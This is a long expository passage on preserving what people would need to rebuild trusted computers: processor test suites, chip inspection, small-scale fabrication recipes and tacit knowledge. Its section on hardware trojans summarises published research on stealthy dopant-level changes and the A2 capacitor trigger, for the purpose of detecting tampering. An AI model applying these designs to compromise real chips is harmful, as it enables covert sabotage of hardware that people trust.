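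Intel estimated that one in nine billion random divisions would give a wrong result. At that rate, a tester would need about 27 billion random divisions for a 95% chance of seeing an error. Tests written to make the circuit read every entry in the table would have found the fault much sooner, but Intel's tests missed it.

Once people knew about the Pentium's division bug, they could check for it with one division. Dividing 4,195,835 by 3,145,727 should give 1.33382, but a flawed Pentium gives 1.33374. Rebuilders can check the result without a trusted computer by multiplying the quotient by 3,145,727 and subtracting the product from 4,195,835, which leaves 0 on a sound processor and 256 on a flawed one. An archive should include a test like this for every famous bug in the processors it covers, since each takes one line.

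### Which test suites to store

Volunteers and standards bodies have already written large sets of tests.

| Suite | What it covers | What it leaves out |
|---|---|---|
| NIST's cryptographic vectors | Hash functions, encryption and digital signatures | Whether the device protects its keys |
| RISC-V architectural tests | The instructions in the standard sets | Many rare combinations of instructions, and speed |
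| Klaus Dormann's 6502 functional test | All documented instructions and the ways they address memory | Undocumented instructions and exact timing |
| Frank Cringle's Z80 exercisers, ZEXDOC and ZEXALL | Most Z80 instructions, with many register values | Interrupts, input and output, and timing |

NIST's test vectors matter because rebuilders will use hashes to check files. One of the simplest gives the SHA-256 hash of the letters `abc`, which begins `ba7816bf`. Others feed each result into the next calculation thousands of times, so a single error makes the final answer wrong.

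The RISC-V tests are short programs that leave their results in memory. The tester compares these with the results from a reference model, a precise description of the instruction set written so that a computer can run it. The archive therefore needs both the tests and the model. Passing shows that the designers understood the specification, but a processor can pass and still have a bug like the Pentium's.

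Cringle's exercisers run many cases of a group of instructions and combine the results into one 32-bit checksum, which they compare with the checksum from a real Z80. This saves a lot of space, but if the checksums differ, rebuilders know only which group failed. ZEXDOC ignores the undocumented parts of the Z80's status register and ZEXALL includes them, so a processor copied faithfully from the datasheet could pass ZEXDOC and fail ZEXALL.

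All three processor suites run on the processor they are testing. A badly broken chip might never start the test, or might print "OK" by mistake, so the first test should need no software. On a 6502, rebuilders can wire the eight data pins to the value EA, the instruction to do nothing. The processor then steps through all 65,536 addresses, taking two clock cycles for each. At 1 MHz, a light on the highest address pin flashes between seven and eight times a second. Later tests should print a checksum to compare with a number on paper, since a faulty chip is far less likely to produce the right checksum than the word "OK".

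### Why tests can't rule out a hidden trigger

Suppose someone has altered a chip so that it misbehaves only when a program loads one particular 64-bit number. There are 2⁶⁴ possible numbers, or about 18 billion billion. A trillion random tries would find the right one with a probability of

10¹² / 2⁶⁴ ≈ 0.00000005,

or about 5 in 100 million. At a billion tries a second, trying half of all the numbers would take 292 years. If the trigger needed two such numbers in a row, even that would be hopeless.

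*Stealthy Dopant-Level Hardware Trojans* (Becker, Regazzoni and colleagues, 2014), the extended version of a 2013 paper, shows that such changes can be very small. The researchers added no circuits and left every wire the same. They changed only the dopants, the impurities that determine how each transistor conducts, in transistors already in the design. One of their examples, as Threatpost's *researchers develop undetectable hardware trojans* reports, was the random number generator from an Intel processor. The change made its output far easier for the attacker to guess, yet the altered design still passed its built-in self-test. The researchers worked from the design and did not alter an actual Intel chip.

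Yang, Hicks and colleagues (2016) tested the A2 attack, the capacitor trick mentioned in connection with FPGAs, by having a complete open-source processor manufactured with the extra circuit inside. The attack worked on the finished chips, and a range of ordinary benchmark programs never triggered it. The capacitor leaks, so it empties and the chip returns to normal unless the right signal keeps repeating quickly. The circuit can be as small as one gate and fits in a gap in the finished layout, whereas a digital counter that did the same job would need hundreds of gates.

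Both demonstrations show only what a dishonest factory could do. Becker and colleagues wrote that nobody had yet reported a hardware trojan in practice. The A2 design assumes that the attacker doesn't know which tests the buyer will run. As with its compilers and bitstreams, an archive loses this protection if an intruder can read its test suites in advance. Rebuilders should therefore add random tests of their own, though these would help only against a carelessly chosen trigger.

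### Opening the chip

Engineers who want to see every transistor and wire have to destroy the chip. Karadağ, Klix and colleagues (2026), in *SoK*, a survey of 187 papers, describe the usual method:

1. Dissolve the plastic package in acid. People often cut one spare chip in half first, to see how thick each layer is.
2. Remove the layers one at a time by etching or polishing, and photograph each with an electron microscope. The surface has to stay flat, and people must stop before they damage the next layer.
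3. Join the overlapping photographs of each layer, then line up the layers.
4. Mark the wires, the transistors and the connections between layers.
5. Work out the netlist, which people can then compare with the one the designers intended.

The preparation and imaging equipment costs millions of dollars. *SAMSEM* (2026), which presents software for tracing the metal wires, says one chip often produces hundreds of gigabytes of images. These could fill several reels of GitHub's film. Such software is also hard to reuse. Karadağ and colleagues tried all 30 published tools and data sets they found, and could reproduce the main results with only seven. An archive's makers shouldn't assume that a program will work because a paper describes it.

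An electron microscope can detect dopant changes too, though Becker's team had assumed it could not. In *Reversing Stealthy Dopant-Level Circuits* (2014), Sugawara, Suzuki and colleagues made a test chip with such changes and could tell all four combinations of dopants apart. They had to photograph a layer close to the transistors, which can take up to 16 times as many images as photographing a metal layer.

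Old chips are much easier to check. The wires in an original 6502 are several micrometres wide, so people can see them through an ordinary optical microscope. Volunteers at the Visual 6502 project photographed an opened chip this way and turned the pictures into a working simulation of every transistor.

X-rays could in principle image a chip without damaging it. *Using a 4-megapixel hybrid photon counting detector* (Fonseca, Levine and colleagues, 2026) describes a machine at NIST that can distinguish details 75 to 80 nanometres across, enough for the 160-nanometre wires in the sample. The researchers still had to grind the chip down to six layers. They scanned about 1,200 cubic micrometres in just over ten hours, and believe two hours would have been enough. At the faster rate, scanning the same six layers of a 10-square-millimetre chip would take about six years. A synchrotron, a particle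 accelerator that produces very bright X-rays, can resolve details of 4 nanometres, but rebuilders are unlikely to have one.

### Looking through the back of a chip

Huang's method, IRIS, is much cheaper. Silicon blocks visible light but lets infrared through from a wavelength of about 1,000 nanometres, and ordinary camera sensors can detect slightly longer wavelengths than that. Huang (2023) shone light of about 1,050 nanometres into the backs of chips and photographed the circuits with lightly modified digital cameras. The chip keeps working and can stay on its circuit board if its back is exposed.

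The long wavelength limits the detail to about a micrometre. The blog post on IRIS shows most of the gates on a chip with 130-nanometre features, so people have a reasonable chance of counting them. On a 22-nanometre chip a gate may be only a few pixels wide, but Huang thinks he could still detect an addition of more than a couple of dozen flip-flops, the circuits that each store one bit. He can't see most of the wires above the transistors. Many of the newest processors carry power through metal on the back, which blocks the view completely.

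For this reason Huang combines IRIS with a scan chain. An altered circuit could return correct results during a scan and behave differently afterwards, but it would need extra gates to do both, and IRIS limits how many gates anyone could have hidden. The combination needs test patterns from the manufacturer. Huang says the check is probabilistic, and he has no formal proof of how much logic could escape detection.

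*On Reading SRAMs in IR Images, and Establishing Bounds on Trust* (bunniestudios, 2026) examines infrared pictures of the author's own 22-nanometre chip, the Baochip-1x. In one memory block he could count 16 column circuits on each side, which matches the 32-bit width in the published source, but the individual rows were too small to see. He concludes that inspection reduces the memory an attacker could hide in a chip from several kilobytes to at most a few dozen bytes. The pictures came from a very expensive laser microscope, though he says a home-made setup shows many of the same details less clearly. He is also judging his own method on his own chip, and nobody has yet tested it on secretly altered samples.

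| Method | Finest detail | Cost or time | Does the chip survive? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Optical microscope, opened chip | Under a micrometre | An ordinary laboratory microscope | No |
| Electron microscope, opened chip | A few nanometres | Millions of dollars | No |
| Laboratory X-rays | 75 to 80 nanometres | Years for a whole chip | No, in NIST's test |
| Synchrotron X-rays | 4 nanometres | A particle accelerator | Yes, in principle |
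| Infrared through the back | About a micrometre | Minutes on Huang's automated machine; he hopes for a price of hundreds to thousands of dollars | Yes |

### How many chips to open

A method that destroys chips can check only a sample, and how many chips rebuilders must open depends on how the attacker worked. If someone altered the factory's master patterns, every chip has the change and opening one is enough. If someone swapped a few chips during shipping, rebuilders could easily miss them.

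CNX Software's *Dabao board features open-source hardware Baochip-1x RISC-V MCU (Crowdfunding)* (2026) gives a price of $899 for a reel of 100 boards with the Baochip-1x. If 10 of the 100 were altered, opening 20 at random would find at least one of the ten about 90% of the time, provided that the examiners recognised the change. If only one board were altered, the chance would be 20%.

Infrared inspection would let the archive's makers photograph all 100 boards and open any chips that look different. They should store the photographs with the boards, along with pictures of a chip they have opened and compared with its design. Rebuilders with a modified camera could check whether a board still matches its picture.

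## What must be recorded to make chips again?

Rebuilders who run out of chips they trust will have to make new ones. They will need a process recipe, which is a factory's instructions for making a chip. It lists the order of the steps, the materials, times and temperatures, and the measurements used to check whether each step worked. People often confuse this with a process design kit, which designers use to find out what a particular factory can make. Several chip makers have published design kits since 2020 but kept their recipes private.

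### What an open design kit contains

SkyWater, an American chip maker, worked with Google to publish a design kit for its 130-nanometre process. According to SkyWater, the kit contains design rules, setup files for design software, models of the basic components and libraries of ready-made logic circuits. The rules set limits such as the narrowest wire the factory can form. The models predict how much current a transistor of a given size will carry. With these files, a designer can turn Verilog into a layout that the factory will accept.

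*Trustless TEE*, a forum's list of open kits, also includes a kit from GlobalFoundries for a 180-nanometre process and one from the German research institute IHP for a 130-nanometre process that suits radio circuits as well as logic.

| Question | Design kit | Process recipe |
|---|---|---|
| How narrow can a wire be? | Yes | As a target to check |
| How much current will this transistor carry? | Yes | As a target to check |
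| How hot is the furnace, and for how long? | No | Yes |
| Which gases, acids and resists does the factory use? | No | Yes |
| How does the operator know that a step has worked? | No | Yes |

The SkyWater kit is unfinished even as a design kit. In August 2026, SkyWater's documentation still described it as an experimental preview not to be used for production, although the factory had made many commercial products with the underlying process.

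One project, LibreSilicon, set out to publish a process as well as a kit. In *Breaking the microchip monopoly*, its developers leviathanch, chipforge and foshardware explain that they started with 1-micrometre features because textbooks still document that technology well. An archive's makers should choose an old technology for the same reason. The developers describe their process in the slides as "almost done", so it was not yet a tested recipe.

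### What happened when Efabless closed

A production run costs too much for most small designers, so they share one, called a shuttle. Until it closed in early 2025, a company called Efabless organised the shuttles to SkyWater's factory. One customer was Tiny Tapeout, which combines hundreds of small designs on one chip. Its *Efabless shuts down* reported that one batch of its chips was waiting for packaging and another was still in the factory. In *Open Source Silicon Project Tiny Tapeout Hits Trouble*, Matt Venn of Tiny Tapeout said he didn't know whether these chips, which hundreds of people had worked on, would ever arrive.

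Tiny Tapeout cancelled its next run. Jeff DiCorpo and Mohamed Kassem then founded ChipFoundry, which took over the batch that was waiting for packaging and reopened access to SkyWater. By September 2025 it had a new run of 237 designs in production, according to Tiny Tapeout's *And the best-looking chip goes to* (2025). The service is still fragile. Tiny Tapeout says ChipFoundry's shuttles go ahead only if customers take at least half the places.

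Tim Ansell, who had started Google's free shuttles in 2021, founded a second service, wafer.space, whose chips are made by GlobalFoundries. Tiny Tapeout's *Wafer.space* listed a price of $7,000 for 1,000 chips. Tiny Tapeout's *wafer.space GF180* later confirmed that the first chips worked, announced another run for June 2026 and listed prices from $4,000 per 1,000 chips. For 2026, Tiny Tapeout planned a run every quarter with IHP, GlobalFoundries or SkyWater, so designers no longer depended on a single company.

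The SkyWater kit stayed online throughout, but designers who had relied on Efabless could do little with it until someone restored access to the factory. Rebuilders without any factory would have the same problem permanently. An open kit is therefore most useful before the disaster. An archive's makers could use one now to order 1,000 copies of a simple processor, store its complete layout in the archive, and check the chips against that layout with Huang's infrared method.

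### From a wafer to a working transistor

A transistor on a chip is a switch. It has two regions of silicon, the source and the drain, which contain impurities that let them conduct. The strip between them normally blocks current. A thin layer of glass (silicon dioxide) covers the strip, and a conductor, the gate, sits on top of the glass. A voltage on the gate attracts charge into the strip, which lets current flow between the two regions.

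University teaching labs have published some of the most complete recipes. Stanford's *2017 SNF410-Depletion Mode NMOS (Option PWell) Flow Run Sheet* (2017) describes a student process that makes only NMOS transistors, in which electrons carry the current. Nearly all modern chips use CMOS, which combines these with transistors of the opposite type to save power. Shulaker and Park, in *A quick turnaround device process*, count seven patterned layers and four rounds of doping in the CMOS process that Stanford taught before. The core NMOS process has three rounds of doping, and they wanted students to finish it in under five days. Rebuilders should also start with NMOS because it is simpler to make.

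| Step | Materials | Equipment | What to measure |
|---|---|---|---|
| Wafer | Polished silicon crystal, cleaning acids, pure water | Acid-proof baths | Resistivity (5 to 10 ohm-centimetres at Stanford) |
| Oxidation | Oxygen or steam | Quartz tube furnace | Temperature and oxide thickness |
| Resist and exposure | Photoresist and developer | Spinner, hotplate, ultraviolet projector | Film thickness, light dose, width of a test line |
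| Etching | Dilute hydrofluoric acid, for oxide | Plastic containers, fume extraction | Thickness removed per minute |
| Doping | Boron, phosphorus or arsenic | Furnace or ion implanter | Resistance of the doped layer |
| Metal | Aluminium | Vacuum chamber | Thickness and resistance |
| Test | A good chip for comparison | Fine probes, power supply, meters | Current at each gate voltage |

Sam Zeloof, who made chips in his family's garage, has published the fullest account of carrying out these steps on a small scale. His first chip, Z1, needed four exposures and 66 steps, which took about 12 hours.

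**The wafer.** An archive should store wafers, because making them is a separate industry with its own recipe. It means purifying silicon to roughly one foreign atom in a billion, growing a single crystal from the melt, then sawing and polishing it. *Zeloof Z1 process* (q3k, 2025), an entry in an open map of what chip making depends on, starts with a bare or ready-coated wafer. In *Second IC*, Zeloof says he bought 25 wafers, each 200 millimetres across, for $45. They have room for about 60,000 chips of 12 square millimetres, the size of Intel's first processor, the 4004.

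**Oxidation.** The operator heats the wafer in oxygen or steam, which turns its surface into silicon dioxide. Thick oxide keeps dopants out of the silicon beneath it, and thin oxide insulates the gate.

**Photoresist and exposure.** Photoresist is a liquid that changes when ultraviolet light hits it. The operator spins the wafer to spread the liquid evenly, bakes it, projects a pattern onto it and washes away the exposed parts. In *IC Design Tools*, Zeloof used 3.5 millilitres at 3,500 turns a minute for 30 seconds, leaving a film about 3.5 micrometres thick. The manufacturer recommended 135 millijoules of light per square centimetre. His projector supplied 4.05 milliwatts per square centimetre, so he needed 135 / 4.05 ≈ 33 seconds. The archive should record the recommended dose as well as the exposure time, because a lamp of different intensity would need a different time.

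Photoresist is the hardest chemical to obtain. Zeloof found that suppliers wouldn't ship it to a private address, and some modern kinds cost more than $8,000 a gallon. It also deteriorates in storage. He spent about two weeks trying to make poly(vinyl cinnamate), a resist that Bell Labs and Kodak developed in the early days of chip making, but didn't finish. The archive's makers should finish that work, because every patterned layer requires photoresist.

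**Etching.** Hydrofluoric acid dissolves oxide wherever the resist has left it bare. Zeloof says to etch for 15 minutes in 1 to 2% acid, or until the surface repels water. Because bare silicon repels water and oxide doesn't, the operator can see when to stop even if the acid is weaker than expected. Recipes should include a visible sign like this wherever one exists. They should also include first-aid instructions, since burns from stronger hydrofluoric acid can kill.

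**Doping.** Stanford's sheet specifies ion implantation, in which a machine fires atoms into the wafer. The source and drain receive 2 × 10¹⁵ arsenic atoms per square centimetre at 60,000 electronvolts, with the wafer tilted by 7 degrees. Zeloof had no implanter, so he put a material containing boron or phosphorus on or near the wafer and heated both in a furnace, so that the atoms spread into the silicon. He got the boron from an insect killer. His method is less precise than implantation but much simpler.

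**Metal.** The operator evaporates aluminium in a vacuum so that it condenses on the wafer, then etches it into wires. The molten aluminium corroded the tungsten holders Zeloof heated it in, and they kept failing until he used thicker ones. His metal also had twice the resistance of pure aluminium, probably because it had absorbed oxygen.

People usually begin testing with single transistors, then connect a few into a ring that switches itself on and off. A three-stage ring made from Z1's transistors ran at about 5,000 cycles a second.

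Much of Stanford's run sheet would still be useless to rebuilders. One step is to coat the wafers with "program 7", and another is to etch for 40 seconds with the program "Poly Etch", but the settings for these programs are stored in the machines. A different step gives the gas flow, pressure, power and time, which someone could reproduce on other equipment. Notre Dame's *Lab procedure* has separate instructions for each machine, and Saraswat's *EE410 CMOS Process Documents* (2008) includes a section on the lab's best practices. An archive needs all of this, with every stored program written out. Even then, the same settings may give different results on another machine, which is why Intel built new factories as exact copies of working ones.

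### How long should the wafer stay in the furnace?

As oxide grows, oxygen has to travel through it to reach fresh silicon, so growth slows down. In 1965 Bruce Deal and Andrew Grove, who worked at Fairchild Semiconductor, described this with the equation

x² + Ax = B(t + τ),

where x is the thickness and t is the time. A and B depend on the temperature, the gas and the direction of the crystal. The last term, τ, allows for oxide that is already there and is zero for bare silicon.

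Stanford's process needs 30 nanometres, or 0.030 micrometres, of oxide at 900 °C. For dry oxygen and the usual crystal direction, A is about 0.423 micrometres and B about 0.00401 square micrometres per hour. Starting from bare silicon,

t = (0.030² + 0.423 × 0.030) / 0.00401 ≈ 3.4 hours.

Stanford's sheet specifies 2 hours 34 minutes. The equation overestimates the time because the first few tens of nanometres, the thickness a gate needs, grow faster in dry oxygen than it predicts. Rebuilders could use the equation to choose a trial time, but they would then have to measure the result and adjust. The archive should record times from a real furnace as well as the equation.

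By the same equation, a furnace 10 °C too hot would grow about 35 nanometres instead of 30. The recipe must therefore include a way to check the thermometer, for instance by melting a piece of silver, whose melting point is 962 °C.

Stanford measures oxide thickness at five points on a test wafer with an optical instrument. Zeloof used colour to estimate that one gate oxide was about 75 nanometres thick. The same colours recur as the oxide gets thicker, and printed colour charts fade, so the archive should also hold a few reference wafers with oxide of known thickness.

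### What small groups have made

Zeloof made his first chip, an amplifier called Z1, in 2018, while he was still at school, and his second, Z2, in 2021. Students and staff at Carnegie Mellon University began the Hacker Fab in 2023 to design cheap chip-making equipment and publish the plans. *HackerFab the opensource semiconductor fab* (2023) put the lab's cost at $70,000 and its area at 600 square feet.

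| | Z1 | Z2 | Hacker Fab |
|---|---|---|---|
| Transistors per chip | 6 | 100 | Mostly single test transistors |
| Gate length | 175 micrometres, later under 5 | 10 micrometres | 5 micrometres |
| Result | A working amplifier | At least one of 15 chips worked fully | Hundreds of devices |
| Taken from industry | Wafers, photoresist, chip packages, projector and microscope parts, a donated machine for attaching wires | Wafers with two layers already on them, dopant, photoresist | Projector, camera, lenses, microcontroller, photoresist, a PC |

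Z2 is weaker evidence of independence than its 100 transistors suggest. Its gates are polysilicon, which factories usually deposit from silane, a toxic and explosive gas. Zeloof avoided using silane by buying wafers that already had the polysilicon on them, along with the gate oxide, which he calls the most fragile layer. The earlier Z1 is better evidence because he grew its gate oxide himself, although transistors he made on the same day could behave very differently.

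The Hacker Fab's main achievement is its stepper, the machine that projects the pattern. *A low-cost, open-source maskless photolithography stepper for microfabrication* (Gonzalez, Bourcart and colleagues, 2025, revised September 2026) describes one that costs about $3,000, while the cheapest commercial machine in its comparison costs $100,000. The Hacker Fab's stepper can form features of 2 micrometres and align one layer with another to within 5 micrometres. It patterns an area of 1.04 by 0.58 millimetres at a time, so a chip the size of the 4004 would need at least 20 joined exposures for each layer. The software can join exposures automatically on a chip's first layer, but the team hasn't finished the version that also aligns later layers.

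Other groups have copied the work. Gonzalez and colleagues report that students at the University of Waterloo and the University of California, Irvine, have built the stepper. Copying takes time, though. Illinois MicroTech's *HackerFab* says that students at the University of Illinois spent their first term setting up equipment and projecting a single letter onto a wafer. Zeloof prototyped early ideas for the stepper, so his chips and the Hacker Fab's aren't fully independent evidence.

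The stepper's projector contains a chip with a huge number of tiny moving mirrors, far beyond what the Hacker Fab can make, and the supplier often runs out of the projector board. Rebuilders therefore face another loop, because they need an advanced chip to make a simple one. Engineers in the early 1970s avoided this by cutting the pattern for each layer by hand from large sheets of plastic film and shrinking it with a camera. An archive should describe that method or hold finished glass masks for the first few chips.

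These projects show that a few people can make transistors as small as those of the early 1970s if they can buy wafers and photoresist. Nobody has yet used this equipment to make a processor.

### Why chips should start small

A speck of dust in the wrong place can ruin a chip. Zeloof photographed particles that had caused short circuits through his thin gate oxide, and had to grow thicker oxide, which meant that the transistors needed a higher voltage. If harmful defects land at random, with an average of D per square centimetre, then a chip of area A has an average of AD defects. The chance that it has none, which is the yield, is

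Y = exp(−AD).

The 4004 has an area of about 0.12 square centimetres. With 5 defects per square centimetre, AD, the average number of defects per chip, is 0.6 and about 55% of the chips are good. With 50, AD is 6 and only about 0.25% are good, or one in 400. The Hacker Fab stepper takes pieces of silicon up to 1 centimetre square, with room for about six such chips. Rebuilders would get about three good processors from each piece at the lower defect density, but would have to process about 67 pieces to get one good processor at the higher density.

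Zeloof's results suggest that a garage may be worse than either. Each of his Z2 chips has an area of 2.4 square millimetres, and a 4004 would be five times as large. If exactly one in 15 Z2s worked, a 4004 would work with probability (1/15)⁵, or about one in 760,000. This is probably too pessimistic, since he hadn't tested every chip and was still improving the process, but it shows how much harder it is to make a chip with the 4004's 2,300 transistors than one with 100.

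Rebuilders could get round this problem by making small chips with a few gates each, testing them, throwing away the bad ones and wiring the rest into a processor, as the Gigatron's designers did with bought chips. By the same formula, a chip of 1 square millimetre has a yield of about 61% at 50 defects per square centimetre. Rebuilders should attempt a whole processor on one chip only when the defect density falls to about 5 per square centimetre.

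The 6502 would then be a better target than the 4004. It is only slightly larger, at about 0.17 square centimetres, and would have a yield of about 43%. It uses NMOS and can run Collapse OS, which the 4004 can't. The Visual 6502 project's photographs already show its layout.

Memory may be a bigger problem than the processor. Collapse OS needs 8 KB to assemble itself, which is 65,536 bits. Intel's first successful dynamic memory chip, from 1970, held 1,024 bits, so rebuilders would need 64 of these chips. Project Oberon's 1 MB would take 8,192 chips.

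No group like this could make modern chips. A phone processor has an area of about 1 square centimetre, so 5 defects per square centimetre would leave fewer than 1% of them working. In practice none would work, because a particle too small to harm a 10-micrometre wire can cover dozens of modern ones, so a room clean enough to limit 1971 chips to 5 harmful defects per square centimetre would cause far more in modern chips. The recipe would also have over a thousand steps.

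### Computing without chips

Rebuilders can make a computer from any switch that a signal can turn on and off. Engineers built useful computers from three kinds of these switches before the first microprocessor.

| Switch | Example | Speed | Memory | What is hard to make |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Relay | Zuse's Z3 (1941), about 2,600 relays | About one addition a second | 176 bytes | Thousands of reliable contacts |
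| Valve | EDSAC (1949), about 3,000 valves | About 650 instructions a second | About 1 KB | Vacuum-tight glass and long-lasting cathodes |
| Separate transistor | PDP-8 (1965), about 1,400 transistors and 10,000 diodes | About 300,000 additions a second | 6 KB | Pure silicon or germanium |
| Simple chip | Intel 4004 (1971), about 2,300 transistors | About 90,000 instructions a second | On separate chips | Everything in the process above |

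A relay computer could do sums for a survey or a timetable, but it would take about a day to do what the 4004 does in a second. A valve computer could calculate hashes and run short programs, though it would use several kilowatts and need regular repairs.

Separate transistors are a much better fallback. The PDP-8, which was built from them, was faster than the 4004. Its makers also tested each part before assembly, so they lost only one transistor when one was bad, instead of a whole processor. Its memory consisted of small magnetic rings threaded on wires, which need no semiconductors. A group that had got as far as the Hacker Fab could aim for a machine like this before trying to make a processor on one chip. The difficulty is the labour of making, testing and soldering more than 10,000 parts.

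### When to store chips instead of a recipe

For most archives, storing finished chips is a better investment than storing instructions for making them. At wafer.space's price, 1,000 finished chips cost $4,000. The Hacker Fab's lab cost many times that and has not produced a processor. If a community had 100 computers and each needed a new processor every ten years, 1,000 spares would last a century, provided they survived storage. The case for storing memory chips is stronger still, because they are as easy to store as processors and far harder to make.

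A recipe becomes worth the effort if rebuilders need more chips than anyone stored, have lost the stock, or no longer trust it, for example because an adversary might have tampered with the factory that made it. The archive's makers can reduce the risk of tampering by buying from several factories and including chips older than the adversary. They should still include a recipe, because documents for a simple NMOS process take up very little space. But they should spend their money first on chips, then on wafers, and finally on furnaces and steppers.

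## What cannot be written down, and who must be trained?

People who have never made a chip may fail even with a complete recipe, because practitioners know things that aren't in their documents. Sociologists call this tacit knowledge. Riding a bicycle is the usual example. Most riders can't explain how they do it, so they teach children by showing them and letting them practise.

### Copying a laser from published papers

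In the early 1970s Harry Collins, a sociologist, studied physicists trying to copy a new carbon dioxide laser called the TEA laser. The journals had good information on how to build one. But as Collins recalls in Physics Today's *Q&A* (2021), everyone who relied on the articles alone built something that looked like a laser but didn't work. The people who succeeded had all spent time in a laboratory with a working laser.

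His 1985 account makes the slightly weaker claim that every successful builder had learned something crucial through personal contact. Nobody succeeded by learning from a go-between who hadn't built a laser, and some people failed even after long contact with someone who had.

One missing detail was the length of the lead between the laser's upper electrode and the large capacitor that supplies its energy. Physicists who had visited a working laboratory built an awkward metal frame to hold the capacitor close to the electrode. The circuit diagram was correct but showed the lead only as a line, so physicists who had nothing else to work from naturally put the heavy capacitor on the bench, which made the lead too long. A lead that long has so much inductance that the current rises too slowly for the laser to fire.

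The builders could tell they had succeeded when the beam made the laboratory wall smoke. Collins also studied physicists trying to detect gravitational waves. They had no such sign, and disagreed about whether a good detector should detect anything.

Most of a rebuild is easy to check, since a compiler or a circuit board visibly works or doesn't. Hidden changes in a chip are harder to check for, because an inspector who finds none may have a clean chip or a poor technique. The archive should therefore include practice chips, some of which its makers have altered, and a sealed envelope listing the altered ones.

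### Why documents leave things out

*Tacit Knowledge, Trust and the Q of Sapphire* (Collins, 2001) describes a later case. Q measures how long a crystal rings after it is set vibrating. For about 20 years, a group in Moscow had been reporting values of up to 400 million for sapphire, but nobody in the West had got above about 50 million.

Physicists from Glasgow spent a week in Moscow in 1998, and one of the Russians then spent a week in Glasgow, but the Glasgow group still couldn't measure a high quality factor for sapphire. They tried 20 ways of suspending a piece he had left behind, then learned from him that it was worse than he had said. They finally measured a quality factor of more than 100 million in June 1999, when he visited for another week. One of the Glasgow physicists later repeated the measurement at Stanford without any Russians present.

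Collins lists five kinds of knowledge that people pass on through contact like this. The last column of the table suggests what an archive could do about each.

| Kind | Why documents omit it | What the archive's makers can do |
|---|---|---|
| Concealed | The expert keeps a trick secret, or the journal has no room for it | Persuade the expert to write it out in full |
| Mismatched salience | The expert doesn't realise the learner needs telling, and the learner doesn't know what to ask | Have beginners follow the instructions, and add answers to all their questions |
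| Ostensive | People have to see or feel the thing itself | Store samples, photographs and film |
| Unrecognised | The expert does something important without knowing that it matters | Film the whole job, and store the equipment the expert used |
| Uncognised | The expert can do it but doesn't know how | Train people alongside the expert |

Some skills become unnecessary once manufacturers build them into equipment. Dennis, in *Tacit Knowledge as a Factor in the Proliferation of WMD*, gives the example of PCR, a method of copying DNA. Each laboratory once depended on a technician with "golden hands", but now it can buy a machine. An archive's makers can similarly store finished flash programmers as well as instructions for building them, provided someone can repair the programmers.

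The Glasgow group kept going through months of failure because they trusted the Russian visitor. A physicist told Collins that another laser, the helium-neon type, takes so much patience to start that nobody would believe it could work unless they already knew it did. Rebuilders will need the same confidence, so the archive should include evidence that each procedure has worked, such as a film of the result and a finished sample.

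### Would people forget how to build a bomb?

MacKenzie and Spinardi (1995) argued in *Tacit Knowledge, Weapons Design, and the Uninvention of Nuclear Weapons* that if weapons designers stopped work and trained no successors, nuclear weapons would, in a qualified sense, be uninvented. Anyone who wanted them again would have to redo much of the inventing.

A later version of the argument, in MacKenzie's *Knowing Machines*, draws on interviews with nearly 50 current and former staff of weapons laboratories and on the history of several national programmes. The first plan for the Los Alamos laboratory, which designed the first atomic bombs, provided for 18 physicists and 20 assistants. Less than three years later, it had about 3,000 technical staff, partly because it had also taken on purifying plutonium. Soviet scientists set out to copy the American design from a spy's detailed description,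 but they took four years, slightly longer than the Americans.

Dennis adds the case of Livermore, a second American weapons laboratory. Its designers had all of Los Alamos's documents, but their first two tests failed.

This evidence is suggestive, but other causes could explain much of it. The Soviet Union had to build a nuclear industry after a devastating war, and Livermore was trying new designs and materials. MacKenzie and Spinardi also concede that later builders would know how hard the task was, could draw on skills from related industries, and might find a simpler design. In *Isn't it time we forgot about the atomic bomb?*, they accept that people willing to take shortcuts might build a crude device fairly quickly.

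Nautilus' *How Three Students Designed an Atomic Bomb* describes a test at Livermore in which three young physicists with no weapons experience had to design a bomb from unclassified sources. They produced a design, but nobody had to build it.

Dennis concludes that a lack of tacit knowledge probably wouldn't stop a weapons programme but would make it slower, more expensive and more likely to fail early on. The same is probably true of computers, though the effect depends on how much time and material a failed attempt wastes. Programmers can correct a mistake and try again within minutes, while a failed wafer uses up days of work and scarce chemicals. Tacit knowledge should therefore matter least for software, more for repairing electronics and most for making chips.

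### Fogbank and the missing impurity

Fogbank is a secret material used in some American nuclear warheads. According to The War Zone's *Fogbank Is Mysterious Material Used In Nukes*, the US government decided in 2000 to make it again for a refurbished warhead, the W76-1, but had by then lost almost all knowledge of how. The US Government Accountability Office later found that the government had kept few records of the original process and that nearly all the experts had left. It put the extra cost at $69 million and the delay to the warheads at about a year.

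When engineers first tried to make Fogbank again, the material didn't come out right. Historic Mysteries explains that modern cleaning methods were removing a substance that had given the original an essential impurity. Production began in 2008, after the engineers worked this out. Historic Mysteries is a weak source, but Nuclear Watch New Mexico's *Curating the Stockpile*, which refers readers to the Los Alamos laboratory's own article, also says an impurity was the answer.

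Fuller records might not have prevented this, because the original makers didn't know the impurity mattered. A jar of the original raw material would probably have helped more, since chemists could have compared it with the new material. An archive that includes a chip recipe should therefore hold a sealed sample of each chemical, along with its supplier, its grade and an analysis of its impurities.

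Nuclear Watch New Mexico argues that recovering the process only required making it a priority. That is encouraging, but the engineers had money, modern laboratories and working suppliers.

### Intel's exact copies

Chip makers used to improve a process while moving it to a new factory. Intel (1998) describes how this became risky as chips got more complicated. During one transfer, a reliability problem delayed a new factory by three months, and its yields took about a year to match the original's. Engineers found that air pressure and the temperature of the rinsing water affected the chips. The length of a cooling hose once had a catastrophic effect.

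Intel responded with a rule called "Copy EXACTLY!". Engineers had to copy everything that might affect the process, down to the number of bends in a pipe, unless this was physically impossible or a change had an overwhelming benefit. An Intel executive says in STVP's *Copy Exactly* (2024), the transcript of a talk, that the factories even have the same paint and tiles. The engineers compared the old and new factories at four levels:

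1. **Inputs**, such as gas flow, temperature and pressure.
2. **The result of each step**, such as the thickness of a film.
3. **Test structures** on the wafer, which show whether several steps work together.
4. **The finished chip.**

If the factories didn't match at one level, the engineers had to find the cause before going on. They weren't allowed to compensate by adjusting something else, because that might change a property nobody was measuring.

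The rule also made faults easier to find. When metal wires in one new factory had a subtle defect, the engineers had only a few differences to investigate, and within a week they traced it to a typing error in a recipe. Intel says that two new factories matched the original's yields from the start. This is the company's own account, and other improvements may have contributed, but the cooling hose closely resembles Collins's capacitor lead.

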